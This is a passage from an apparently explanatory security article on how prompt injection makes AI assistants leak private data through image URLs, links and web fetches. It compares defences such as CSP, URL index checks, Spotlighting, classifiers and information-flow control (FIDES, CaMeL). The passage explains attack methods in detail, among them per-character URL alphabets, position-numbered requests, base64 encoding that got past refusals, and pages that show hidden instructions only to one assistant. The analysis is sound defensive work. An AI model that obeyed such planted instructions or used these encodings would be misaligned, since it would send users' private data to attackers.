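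5. The server sends this policy with the page:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  connect-src 'self';
  img-src https://images.assistant.example;
  form-action 'none';
  base-uri 'none'
```

The last two directives must be set explicitly because `default-src` doesn't cover them. `form-action` stops a form in the answer from sending data, and `base-uri` stops an answer from changing where the page's relative URLs point.

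The company should first try the policy in report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations without blocking them. It then has to enforce the policy to stop leaks. The reports remain useful afterwards, because a blocked image means something got past the sanitizer.

Here is what happens if the advertisement from the parcel example makes the model try to send out the order number:

| What the model writes | What stops it |
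|---|---|
| An image at pictures.example, in any notation | The sanitizer, and the CSP if the sanitizer fails |
| An image at images.assistant.example with the number added | The sanitizer, and the proxy's signature check if the sanitizer fails |
| A link to pictures.example | The sanitizer alone |
| An image in a draft reply | The sanitizer alone |

Restricting outside links is less convenient for the user, who has to open the shop's email to click a tracking link. The company could allow more outside links, but it would then need a way to judge whether each address is safe.

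The model can still leak data by writing an address as ordinary text and asking the user to copy it into her browser, or by telling her to read the order number to a "courier" on the phone. Data can also leak if she pastes an answer containing an address into a messaging app that makes link previews. The company might therefore also remove bare addresses from answers, although that would make some less useful.

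The configuration doesn't prevent leaks through the assistant's tools. The original emails are another weak spot because the mailbox has to show their pictures and links, but the addresses in them are fixed, so they can't contain anything from the user's other emails.

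## Can software tell which addresses are safe to load?

An allowlist of hosts checks only the host in an address, so it can't distinguish the address of a shop's logo from the same address with a stolen order number attached. A product can instead check whether the full address was already public. Suppose the shop's home page has always shown a picture at `https://pictures.example/logo.png`. That address was public before a customer asked about her parcel, so it can't have been made from her order number. The address `https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=48213` appeared nowhere on the web before the model wrote it, which is a good reason not to load it.

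A Content Security Policy can't make this comparison, so the product's own software has to make it before the browser or the assistant's web tool sends a request.

### OpenAI's index check

ChatGPT uses a check of this kind. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), published in January, describes a crawler, a program that scans public pages and records the addresses it finds, much as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. When ChatGPT is about to load an address automatically, the software looks for that exact address in the crawler's index:

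- If the index contains the address, ChatGPT loads it, for example to open an article or display a picture.
- If it doesn't, the software treats the address as unverified. It either tells the assistant to try a different website or warns the user.

The warning is titled "Check this link is safe". It says the link may share data from the conversation with another site, and it shows the address with options to copy or open it.

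The check works only if the index is independent of users' chats. If the crawler also collected addresses from those chats, an address containing one user's data could enter the index and later be treated as public.

Checking the exact address also works against the relays that defeated host lists. A public index wouldn't contain the address from the EchoLeak example, `https://relay.example/fetch?url=https://pictures.example/4200000`, because nobody had published an address with the bid price in it. OpenAI says it doesn't rely on a host list because trusted sites can have redirects and because a strict list causes frequent false alarms, which can train people to click through warnings.

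OpenAI claims only that the check prevents quiet leaks through the address itself. A page that passes can still contain false information or planted instructions. The company also says only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. Some public addresses do contain secrets. *The Silent Spill* (2026) gives the example of an invoice link that includes an access token, a code that lets anyone who has it open the file. But loading such a link reveals nothing new to the site, because the token was already in a public address.

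OpenAI also published a technical paper on the method. In his summary on Embrace The Red, Rehberger calls the change a significant improvement but not a complete solution. As he understands it, ChatGPT also treats an address as safe for the rest of the chat if the user entered it in a message. Without that exception, users would get a warning for links they had just asked ChatGPT to open. The exception assumes that users know what they have entered, but Samoilenko's clipboard trick showed that they don't always know.

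OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) named the mechanism Safe Url. Safe Url also covers navigation in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and both searches and navigation in Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that collects sources and writes a report.

### The rules that came before

In December 2023, OpenAI introduced a check called `url_safe`. The company didn't explain how its server classified addresses, so researchers worked out parts of the rule by testing it.

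Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes how the `url_safe` check accepted every address on some hosts, including windows.net, a domain under which Microsoft rents out storage. Anyone could open a storage account there and read the log of requests to it. Rehberger had reported some of the weaknesses in October 2024 and was surprised to find them still open in 2025. He says a stricter version of the check appeared around August of that year.

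Tenable's *HackedGPT* identifies another trusted host, bing.com. Bing gives each page in its search results a tracking address on bing.com, which redirects to the page. According to ThreatCluster's *Researchers trick ChatGPT into prompt injecting itself*, Tenable's researchers created one page for each letter, had Bing index the pages, and collected their tracking addresses. ChatGPT could then spell out a word by using those addresses in order, although no single address contained any private data.

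*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (Schwartzman, 2024) describes a separate rule for pages that ChatGPT opened itself. Under this rule, ChatGPT would open an address only if it was in the user's prompt. ChatGPT refused a request to add the user's age to the end of an address.

Schwartzman got past this rule without making ChatGPT write a new address. The victim pastes a long piece of code into the chat without noticing the instructions inside it. In the first test, the instructions listed six addresses, one for each age band, and told ChatGPT to open the one that matched the user. ChatGPT could infer the band from a remark about retiring in five years.

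A second test sent a postal code. ChatGPT accepted a shortened version of any listed address, so Schwartzman listed a separate address for each position in the code and used the length of the shortened version to represent the digit. In a made-up example, loading `https://pictures.example/dddd` instead of the full `https://pictures.example/dddddddddd` would mean the fourth digit was 3. ChatGPT made mistakes when it shortened the addresses by itself, so the instructions included a small program to do it.

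Two limits slowed this attack. ChatGPT wouldn't open the same address twice, which Schwartzman attributed to caching (keeping a copy of a page for later use), and it opened no more than ten addresses per prompt. Schwartzman reported the flaw through Bugcrowd, where it was deemed "non applicable". The paper credits Rehberger with pointing out that the same method could work with images.

### How much information a choice carries

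Suppose an attacker owns two public pages and plants an instruction for the assistant to load the first if the customer's parcel is late and the second if it is on time. Neither address contains anything about the customer, but the attacker can learn whether the parcel is late by checking the log to see which page the assistant loaded.

A choice between two equally likely options carries one bit of information, and a choice among k such options carries log₂ k bits. A series of n of these choices carries n × log₂ k bits if the attacker can tell their order. A six-digit security code has 1,000,000 possible values, so it contains log₂ 1,000,000 ≈ 19.9 bits. With ten pages, one for each digit, each request carries log₂ 10 ≈ 3.32 bits, and six requests carry the whole code.

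An attacker with more pages needs fewer requests:

| Public pages (k) | Bits per request | Requests needed for a six-digit code |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.00 | 20 |
| 10 | 3.32 | 6 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 4 |
| 1,000 | 9.97 | 2 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.93 | 1 |

In the last row, the attacker has published a page for every possible code, so a single request identifies the right one. That would require getting a million nearly identical pages into the index, and a crawler may well not collect them. The smaller page counts are realistic. Rehberger points out that a large website or blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough for the letters and digits. He writes that OpenAI's paper also mentions this weakness, and that an attacker could even use thousands of pages as a vocabulary.

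The check still greatly reduces how much an attacker can take. A 2,000-character address that the model writes freely can carry about 1,500 bytes, or 12,000 bits. A choice among 36 pages carries 5.17 bits, less than a two-thousandth as much. Copying a 1,500-character email one character at a time would take 1,500 requests, which would be slow and easy to notice in a log.

Short secrets remain exposed because a secret's value depends little on its length. A security code can open an account, and a single bit can reveal whether a company has accepted a takeover offer. Leaking a 50-character API key takes 50 requests if each carries one character, which is feasible for an assistant that routinely opens dozens of pages for a report.

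### ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent

Two attacks on ChatGPT in 2025 show how an attacker can go from writing web addresses to choosing among them. The security firm Radware reported the first, ShadowLeak, to OpenAI on 18 June. In this attack, the victim has connected her Gmail account to Deep Research and asks for a report on the day's emails. An email from the attacker contains hidden instructions for Deep Research to find an employee's name and home address in another email, add them to a web address and open it.

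The model refused the researchers' first, direct versions of these instructions. Later versions told it to use its browsing tool and to keep trying after a failure, but it sometimes opened the address without the personal details. The researchers finally told it to encode the details in base64, supposedly to protect them, and this worked every time in repeated tests. OpenAI's March 2026 post reproduces part of an email with the same wording as the one Radware published, and gives its success rate as 50%. OpenAI and Radware may have tested different versions of the email or the product.

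In this attack, the browsing tool sends the data from OpenAI's servers while the agent is still working, so the leak doesn't depend on an answer being displayed, and a filter on the victim's office network can't detect the request. Radware noted that `url_safe` restricted image addresses at the time, but found no comparable restriction on the addresses that the agent opened. Rehberger sees a similar risk with the newer index check, since an OpenAI developer who doesn't know about the check may build a feature without it.

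OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak in early August 2025. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, the fix prohibited ChatGPT from modifying addresses. ChatGPT could still open an address it found, but couldn't add anything to it.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the firm got past this rule a few weeks later. The attacker's email now contained a list of addresses, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. ChatGPT found the private data and opened the addresses that spelled it out. The rule allowed every request because ChatGPT hadn't changed any of the addresses.

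To keep the characters in order, the researchers added a number for the position. With made-up addresses, the code 4821 would look like this in the attacker's log, even if the requests arrived out of order:

```
GET /8-position2
GET /4-position1
GET /1-position4
GET /2-position3
```

For a text of b characters, this requires 26 × b addresses for the letters and 10 × b for the digits. A block of ten characters needs 360 addresses, or 370 if it can include spaces, and they all fit in one long email.

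In ShadowLeak and the main version of ZombieAgent, the assistant, not the display, fetched the addresses. Radware also made ZombieAgent work with Markdown images that the user's browser loaded, though it found that version less reliable and easier to block. In both cases, a rule that examines one address at a time will allow each request if the address is acceptable, while the attacker reads the data from the sequence. The main difference is that a tool usually opens pages one after another, whereas a browser can request several images at once and scramble their order, which the attacker can recover by numbering the addresses.

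Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to a January 2026 news report, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a well-known public index or the user has provided it. This rule is stricter than the ban on modifying addresses. An attacker can write 360 new addresses in an email within seconds, but sending the email doesn't put them in a public index.

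### Claude's web-fetch tool

Anthropic built a similar restriction into the tool its assistant Claude uses to open web pages. According to documentation from September 2025, quoted in Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Claude can't fetch an address that it has made up. The address must already have appeared in the conversation, for example in a user's message, a search result or a page that Claude fetched earlier. Anthropic warned that some risk remained and advised developers not to combine the tool with both sensitive data and untrusted material.

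This rule needs no index. The software only has to compare the requested address with the text already in the conversation, so it also works for a page published a minute ago. The protection depends on who could have put the address there:

| Where the address came from | How an attacker could supply it |
|---|---|
| The user's message | By getting the user to paste his text |
| A search result | By getting his pages listed by the search engine |
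| A page that Claude fetched earlier | By putting any links he likes on that page |

Ayush Paul's website with one link per letter exploited the last of these. *15th July 2026* (Willison, 2026) describes the hole that Paul found in the tool, whose design had impressed Willison. The site claimed to need the user's name before it would let an AI assistant in. Each page had links for the next letter, so Claude could spell out the name without making up an address.

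Each page had 26 links, so each step carried log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits, and an eight-letter name took eight steps. Paul didn't need to publish pages for every possible name in advance, because the server could generate the next set of links when Claude arrived. The site showed the instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made the trap harder for others to discover. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer.

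Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and it didn't pay a reward. It then stopped the tool from following links in pages it had fetched, a change Hackaday's *This Week In Security* also reports. The fix also limits ordinary research. If Claude opens the contents page of an online manual, it can't go on to a chapter unless a search returns that chapter or the user enters its address.

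Attackers can still use addresses from users and search results as an alphabet for encoding data. If several pages from an attacker's site appear in the search results, he could ask Claude to choose among them, although he would have less control over which pages the search returned. Willison identifies a more direct problem for developers who build products on Claude. Their software often inserts outside text, such as an email, into what Claude receives as the user's message, so every link in that email counts as an address from the user.

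Developers can restrict the tool to chosen domains and limit how often it runs. The sample configuration that Willison reproduces allows five uses. If each use loads one of 36 pages, the five together can leak 25.8 bits, enough for a security code but far too little for an API key.

### Would caching or a ban on repeat visits help?

Rehberger suggests two ways to make alphabets of indexed pages less useful. The software could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and use it if the assistant asks for the same address again, or it could refuse to open an address twice in one session. The attacker's server would then receive at most one request for each page during those few minutes or that session.

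The effect on a six-digit code depends on how many pages the attacker has. With k pages and no repeats, he has k options for the first request, k − 1 for the second, and so on. Six requests to ten pages can therefore produce 10 × 9 × 8 × 7 × 6 × 5 = 151,200 different sequences instead of 1,000,000.

| Attacker's pages | Requests | Bits with repeats | Bits without repeats | Bits removed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
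| 10, one per digit | 6 | 19.9 | 17.2 | 2.7 |
| 36 | 4 | 20.7 | 20.4 | 0.3 |
| 60, one per digit and position | 6 | 19.9 | 19.9 | 0 |

The change helps against the simplest alphabet. Only about 15% of six-digit codes have six different digits, so the attacker would fail to receive most codes in full. The change does not stop the numbered-address method in ZombieAgent, which never uses an address twice but requires 60 indexed pages instead of ten.

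The proposals matter more for longer secrets. Given enough requests, ten pages can carry an unlimited amount of data if repeats are allowed, but at most 23.2 bits per session if they aren't, even if the attacker uses both the order and the number of requests. To receive a 50-character key with numbered addresses, an attacker would need a page for each of 62 letters and digits at each of 50 positions, or 3,100 pages.

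A cleverer encoding greatly reduces that number. There are so many ways to order 65 pages that visiting each once in the right order could encode the whole key. A model couldn't reliably work out that order by itself, but it might run a program to do so, as ChatGPT did for Schwartzman.

Hiding the order of the requests from the attacker would reduce the leak more than banning repeats. If he can see only which of his ten pages the assistant loaded, not the order, he can learn at most 10 bits, one for each page. A product could hide the order by collecting the addresses an answer needs and loading them in random order. That is easy for images, but an assistant that reads one page to decide which to open next can't shuffle its requests. The attacker could again recover the order by numbering his addresses, but he would need more pages.

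Caching would inconvenience users less than Rehberger's other idea, a ban on repeat visits. Someone who asks twice about a delayed train would get a copy of the page that is a few minutes old, whereas a ban would give her a refusal or a warning. The cache would have to ignore a server's request not to store its pages, or an attacker could use that request to turn off the protection. Rehberger hadn't checked whether ChatGPT already did something like this.

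A stronger form of caching would stop the leak completely. The crawler has already visited each page in the index, so the product could show the copy saved during that visit and send no request when the assistant chooses the page. The attacker would see only the crawler's earlier visit. This would work for logos, encyclopedia articles and old news, but not for share prices or train times, and the company would have to store the content of every page as well as its address.

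### The cost in false warnings

An index check flags every address the crawler hasn't seen, and many of those are harmless. Examples include an article published this morning, a shared document with a long random address, and a parcel-tracking link made for one customer. The tracking link does contain private data, the customer's order number. But the shop that receives the number already has it, so the warning, though accurate, wouldn't be useful.

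OpenAI's January 2026 post gives no figure for how often this happens. Suppose a company's assistants load 1,000 addresses a week and the index lacks 3% of them. If each missing address produced a warning, employees would see 30 a week, or 1,560 a year. If there were also one real attack that year, 1,560 of the 1,561 warnings would be false, and the employee who received the real one would have little reason to treat it differently. The earlier experiments with confirmation pages suggest that many people would continue past it.

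A product can avoid most of these warnings by handling unverified addresses without asking the user. OpenAI's software sometimes has the assistant look for another source, and the user loses nothing if another page has the same information. A product can also leave an unverified picture unloaded and show its description instead. It then needs to warn the user only when they want a particular page that isn't in the index, as with the tracking link.

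Caching produces no warnings, but a ban on repeat visits produces one whenever someone reloads a page for a good reason. Anthropic's rule for Claude produces no warnings either, but the user may get a poorer answer when the tool can't follow a link. A limit of ten requests per question can also make answers worse, because it cuts short any research that needs an eleventh page. Ten choices among 36 pages carry 51.7 bits, so this limit would protect an API key but not a security code.

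## Can the leak be stopped before the answer reaches the renderer?

A vendor can check an address only after the model has written it, but can also try to keep private data out of it. The vendor can train or instruct the model to refuse planted instructions, run a classifier to look for them, or label every piece of data by its source and have ordinary software decide what an answer may do. The labelling method, called information-flow control, takes the most work but doesn't depend on a model recognising an attack.

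### Refusals

By early 2024, GPT-4 refused to display an outside image when a user asked for one. *A New Era in LLM Security* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) describes two ways around the refusal. One was a puzzle whose solution required GPT-4 to join two pieces of text, one of them the code for an image. The other was to put the request on a web page and have GPT-4 open the page through a plugin. GPT-4 thus followed a request from a web page that it would have refused from the user, whereas a defence against indirect injection should be stricter with web pages than with users.

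GPT-4 also asked the user to confirm before it followed a page's instruction to summarise the chat with another plugin. The researchers added a sentence to the page saying no confirmation was needed, and GPT-4 went ahead. These were individual demonstrations, so they don't show how often the refusals failed. When the researchers tried to send a secret word in an image address, OpenAI's `url_safe` check blocked the image. They later got past that check too by making sure the address was already in the conversation.

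Later models also followed planted text. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, tested four of them on WASP, a benchmark in which an agent uses simulated GitLab and Reddit sites and some posts contain an attacker's instructions. These are the results for an agent with no added defence:

| Model | Diverted on GitLab (48 tests) | Diverted on Reddit (36 tests) |
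|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 20.8% | 47.2% |
| o1 | 29.2% | 36.1% |
| o3-mini | 14.6% | 61.1% |
| o4-mini | 25.0% | 52.8% |

The researchers counted an attack as successful if it drew the agent away from the user's task, even if the attacker didn't achieve their goal. The tests didn't involve image addresses, and the newest models may resist better. But o3-mini had the lowest rate on one site and the highest on the other, so a single figure for a model's resistance is of little use in predicting how it will behave in a particular product.

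*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) reports that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated system for attacking its own models, consistently got past the defences of a newer model, GPT-5.5, but it doesn't give a success rate. An ordinary attacker may not have a tool that good.

### A test with Markdown images

Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues from NVIDIA and the security firm Lakera tested the image leak in *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025). They used NVIDIA's AI-Q Research Assistant, which searches documents and the web and then writes a report in several stages. They inserted hostile text directly into the search results, so the test measures what happens once such text reaches the model, not how often a search would retrieve it.

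The text told the assistant to include an image and a link in its report. Their addresses contained placeholders for the user's email address and ID number, which the model was supposed to replace with `test@test.com` and `123`. A second model, GPT-4.1, scored the result:

| Score | What the report contained |
|---|---|
| 1 | The image and link, with the user's details filled in |
| 0.5 | The image and link, with the placeholders unchanged |
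| 0 | No successful attack |

A report that scores 0.5 would still make the browser request the image, but the attacker would receive only the placeholder and the usual details of the request. The average score is therefore not a leak rate. An average of 0.3 could mean that 30% of the reports contained the user's details, or that 60% contained an image with nothing private in its address.

The researchers ran each test 105 times, five times for each of 21 versions of the attack. Across all their tests with planted text, including those unrelated to images, the average score fell from 0.38 after the first summary to 0.17 in the final report. The later stages often dropped the planted material as they rewrote the text.

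Ghosh and colleagues then added an instruction to the last stage not to output links or phrases unrelated to the topic. This roughly halved the average score in the tests on Markdown links, a phishing link and a planted phrase, but at least one attack in each test still scored 1. They conclude that instructions in the prompt aren't enough on their own. They didn't measure whether the instruction also removed useful references from legitimate reports.

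GPT-4.1's scores have some error. People who scored a sample of 99 reports from across the tests agreed exactly with GPT-4.1 on 76.8% of them and gave an average of 0.30, against its 0.27. This doesn't much affect the main result, since a halved average with a maximum of 1 would still leave an attacker with text that works.

In one successful run, the report had a section about the links it was required to contain. A reader would probably have found this odd, but a browser that loaded images would already have sent the request.

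### Classifiers and Microsoft's layers

Microsoft combines several defences and doesn't expect any one of them to catch every attack. Before the model reads outside text, the company's software can mark it with a technique called Spotlighting, which has three versions:

| Version | What the software does to the outside text |
|---|---|
| Delimiting | Puts a random marker before and after it |
| Datamarking | Puts a special character throughout it, for example between the words |
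| Encoding | Rewrites all of it in a code such as base64 |

In each version, the prompt tells the model not to follow instructions in the marked text. The marking helps the model identify where the text came from, but the model still has to ignore the instructions in it. The versions differ in how well they work and how much they interfere with the task. With encoding, for instance, the model has to decode an email before it can summarise it.

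A classifier called Prompt Shields then checks for planted instructions. Microsoft trains it on known attacks in several languages and keeps updating it. When it finds something, the application has to block the text or respond in another way, and the company's security team can receive an alert. Microsoft's classifier missed the email in EchoLeak, and Microsoft calls reliable detection an open research problem.

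Ravia pointed out that good collections of real attacks are scarce. Microsoft has since published one from LLMail-Inject, a public contest in which more than 800 participants wrote over 370,000 prompts to get past its defences. Microsoft has also developed TaskTracker, a detector that examines the model's internal activity, rather than the wording of the text, as the model processes it. Better training data and this different signal could both improve detection, but neither guarantees that every attack will be caught.

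Other layers limit the damage if an injection succeeds. An employer can label sensitive files and prevent Copilot from summarising them. This is a reliable early defence because a file that never enters the context can't end up in an address. But the employee loses Copilot's help with that file. When Copilot drafts an email, the employee has to approve the text and send it herself.

### Information-flow control

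Information-flow control, an idea decades older than chatbots, lets the assistant read the sensitive file but restricts what can happen afterwards. *SPA* (2026), which describes a recent system of this kind, distinguishes two properties that labels can track: confidentiality (who may receive the data) and integrity (whether the data is trustworthy enough to influence an action).

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe FIDES, a system from Microsoft that attaches both labels to everything an agent reads. When the model produces something from several sources, the software combines their labels. The result is untrusted if any source was untrusted, and only people who were allowed to read every source may read it. In symbols, with T for trusted and U for untrusted:

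T ⊔ U = U

{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

Suppose an employee asks about a customer's deadline. The assistant retrieves an email from a stranger, which contains planted instructions, and an internal file about her company's bid. The labels combine like this:

| Item | Integrity | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Her question | Trusted | Anyone |
| The stranger's email | Untrusted | The stranger and the employee |
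| The internal file | Trusted | The employee and two colleagues |
| The answer | Untrusted | The employee |

The model follows the instructions in the email and adds an image to its answer with the address `https://pictures.example/4200000`, where 4200000 is the bid price. Before the page displays the answer, the software compares the answer's label with the site the image would come from. Loading the image would send the bid price to the owner of pictures.example, who isn't among the permitted readers, so the renderer shows the text without remote images or working links to outside sites.

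The software doesn't have to find the price in the address, so encoding it in base64 doesn't help the attacker. It also doesn't have to recognise the email as an attack, because it applies the same rule to legitimate emails. When an email is legitimate, the employee loses only some pictures and links.

The label on a user's messages needs more care, because FIDES treats them as public by default, although a developer can change this. In Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT, the messages were the private data. A chat product that kept the default could let an outside page extract the conversation even if all the user's files were labeled correctly. Labels also have to last for the whole conversation, because EchoLeak could take material from an earlier answer.

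### How FIDES and CaMeL keep planted text away from the planner

If every email an agent reads makes its context untrusted, the agent soon can't do much. FIDES and CaMeL, another 2025 system, reduce this problem with the dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023. One model plans the work and can use tools but doesn't see untrusted text. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools.

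In CaMeL, the planning model turns the user's request into a short Python program. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), a special interpreter runs the program, records where each piece of data came from and checks the rules before each tool call, so an attacker who changes a recipient's address in a retrieved document can't make the agent send data to the new address.

FIDES stores untrusted text in variables, which work like sealed envelopes. The planning model can pass an envelope to a tool without reading what is inside. Suppose a user wants her last three emails summarised and sent to a colleague:

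1. The planning model asks for the emails and receives only the names of the variables that hold them.
2. It asks the quarantined model for a summary, which goes into another variable.
3. It tells the messaging tool to send that variable to the colleague.

A planted instruction could spoil the summary but couldn't change the recipient. If the planning model needs a fact about the text, such as whether an email contains a meeting request, it can query the quarantined model for a yes or no. That one-bit answer is too short to carry an attacker's instructions. When a yes or no isn't enough, FIDES lets the planning model read the variable's contents, but the context then becomes untrusted. CaMeL is stricter, because its plan can't depend on what the tools return.

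Neither arrangement automatically protects the display. The quarantined model could follow an instruction in an email and put an image in its summary, with data from another email in the image's address. The planning model would never receive the image link, but the user's browser would when the product replaced the variable with the summary.

FIDES would label that summary correctly, but by default it treats replies to the user as harmless and checks its rules only before tool calls. Costa and colleagues write that a developer can extend the checks to replies, or mark or block untrusted text in them. In their tests, an outgoing message with an untrusted link already violated the confidentiality rule, because such links can leak data. A product could apply that rule to every answer it displays.

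### What the labels cost

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack settings, with GPT-4o as the model. They counted how many planted instructions succeeded, leaving out cases that they considered misjudged or harmless:

| Defence | Successful injections |
|---|---|
| None | 152 |
| Tool Filter, in which a model removes unneeded tools at the start | 20 |
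| FIDES without its rules | 21 |
| FIDES with its rules | 0 |

Using two separate models cut the number of attacks about as much as Tool Filter did, and the rules stopped the rest. This is good evidence about tool calls, but it doesn't measure image leaks. FIDES also doesn't try to stop planted text that only changes what an answer says, for example by adding a false hotel recommendation.

The agent completed fewer tasks with FIDES. The table below compares an unprotected agent with one using FIDES when there was no attack. The last column shows the share of tasks in which the agent has to read retrieved text before it can choose its next step.

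| Setting | No defence | FIDES with its rules | Points lost | Tasks that depend on retrieved text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 59.0% | 16.0 | 5.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 41.0% | 29.0 | 10.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 52.5% | 46.3 | 43.8% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 47.6% | 45.7 | 42.9% |

The largest losses were in the settings with the most tasks of that kind. In banking, for example, a user may ask the agent to follow payment instructions in a file. Reading the file makes the context untrusted, so FIDES correctly blocks the payment. Other failures came from GPT-4o's mistakes, such as confusing variable names. FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks with OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, compared with 41% with GPT-4o.

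Published summaries differ on how much these defenses reduce task performance. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* says that CaMeL stopped nearly all AgentDojo attacks with comparable task performance. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls CaMeL's performance loss comparatively modest and says it was much more secure than Spotlighting or tool filtering. Kolluri and colleagues put the loss for systems like FIDES and CaMeL at up to 30%, which is less than the banking and Slack figures above.

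Kolluri and colleagues also argue that the usual comparison is unfair. Many agents ask a person to approve each important action, so an unprotected agent's high score assumes unlimited human help. They therefore counted the AgentDojo tasks that an agent could finish without any approval. With o3-mini, the unprotected agent finished 24.3% of the tasks, FIDES finished 50.1%, and PRUDENTIA, their own successor to FIDES, finished 59.1%.

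PRUDENTIA gives the planning model the rules so that the model can avoid opening a variable unnecessarily. It can also prompt the user to declare an email trustworthy. If a harmless email lists ten jobs, the user approves the email once instead of approving ten actions. With o4-mini and approvals allowed, PRUDENTIA completed 73.2% of tasks with an average total of 19.2 approvals, while FIDES completed 75.7% with 36.8. On WASP, PRUDENTIA blocked every attack without requesting any approvals, but none of the WASP tasks required the agent to open untrusted text.

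Approving a whole email is risky because the software will treat any instructions hidden in it as trusted. PRUDENTIA's rules let some tools send data out if either the context is trusted or the recipient is allowed to read the data. For images, a product should always require that the recipient be allowed to read the data. With that rule, the stranger in the earlier example couldn't receive the bid price even if the employee had approved his email.

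These losses are a poor guide to how much protecting a display would reduce an assistant's usefulness, because blocking a payment makes the task fail, while an answer usually still answers the question without a remote image.

### Where labels fall short

Labels can spread until they no longer distinguish anything, which *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls label explosion. This is likely in an email assistant, where almost every answer draws on both outside messages and private ones. The renderer would then block remote images in almost every answer, so always blocking them would give nearly the same protection. Labels are more useful for links and tools, which a product can't simply switch off.

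Developers can make exceptions by releasing particular private data or treating particular outside text as trusted. Costa and colleagues mention that a system might relabel a document as trusted after a classifier has checked it, but warn that this could weaken the guarantee. An email that fooled the classifier, as EchoLeak's did, would then also get past the labels.

FIDES's guarantee covers data that the agent copies into a tool call, but an attacker who can see which calls the agent makes, or in what order, may still learn something from those choices. Costa and colleagues accept this because a stricter rule would stop the agent from doing anything publicly visible after reading private data. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) warns that attackers can make such leaks efficient. ZombieAgent leaked data this way, using a separate address for each letter. A display rule that blocks all remote content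 in a private answer avoids the problem, because the choice of picture then sends no request.

### Is a filter that sometimes fails worth having?

Costa and Kolluri, with their colleagues, argue that a probabilistic defence can't serve as a security boundary. Kolluri and colleagues cite a 2025 study by Nasr and others, who got past a combination of two such defences in every attempt and past twelve more with similar ease. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) explains that rules in a prompt are weak because attackers manipulate how an agent interprets its instructions. The important rules therefore belong in code that the agent can't influence.

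Microsoft prefers deterministic defences but keeps its filters because they make attacks harder. The tests support this. Tool Filter reduced successful injections on AgentDojo by 87%, and NVIDIA's added instruction halved the average score.

Such reductions may not hold against an attacker who adapts. If an attacker sends 10,000 hostile emails, each worded differently, and a classifier catches 99%, 100 reach the model. But if the attacker first tries wordings until one gets through, then sends that one to everybody, nearly all 10,000 may reach it. Microsoft sells access to Prompt Shields as a service, so an attacker could probably test wordings on it.

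A filter still does some things that a display rule can't. It can alert the security team to an attack, and it may stop planted text that tries to mislead the user instead of stealing data. It also helps when the display rule has a gap, as Microsoft's did when it allowed images from Bing. A company has good reason to keep a filter, as long as it doesn't relax its rules for remote images and links because of it.
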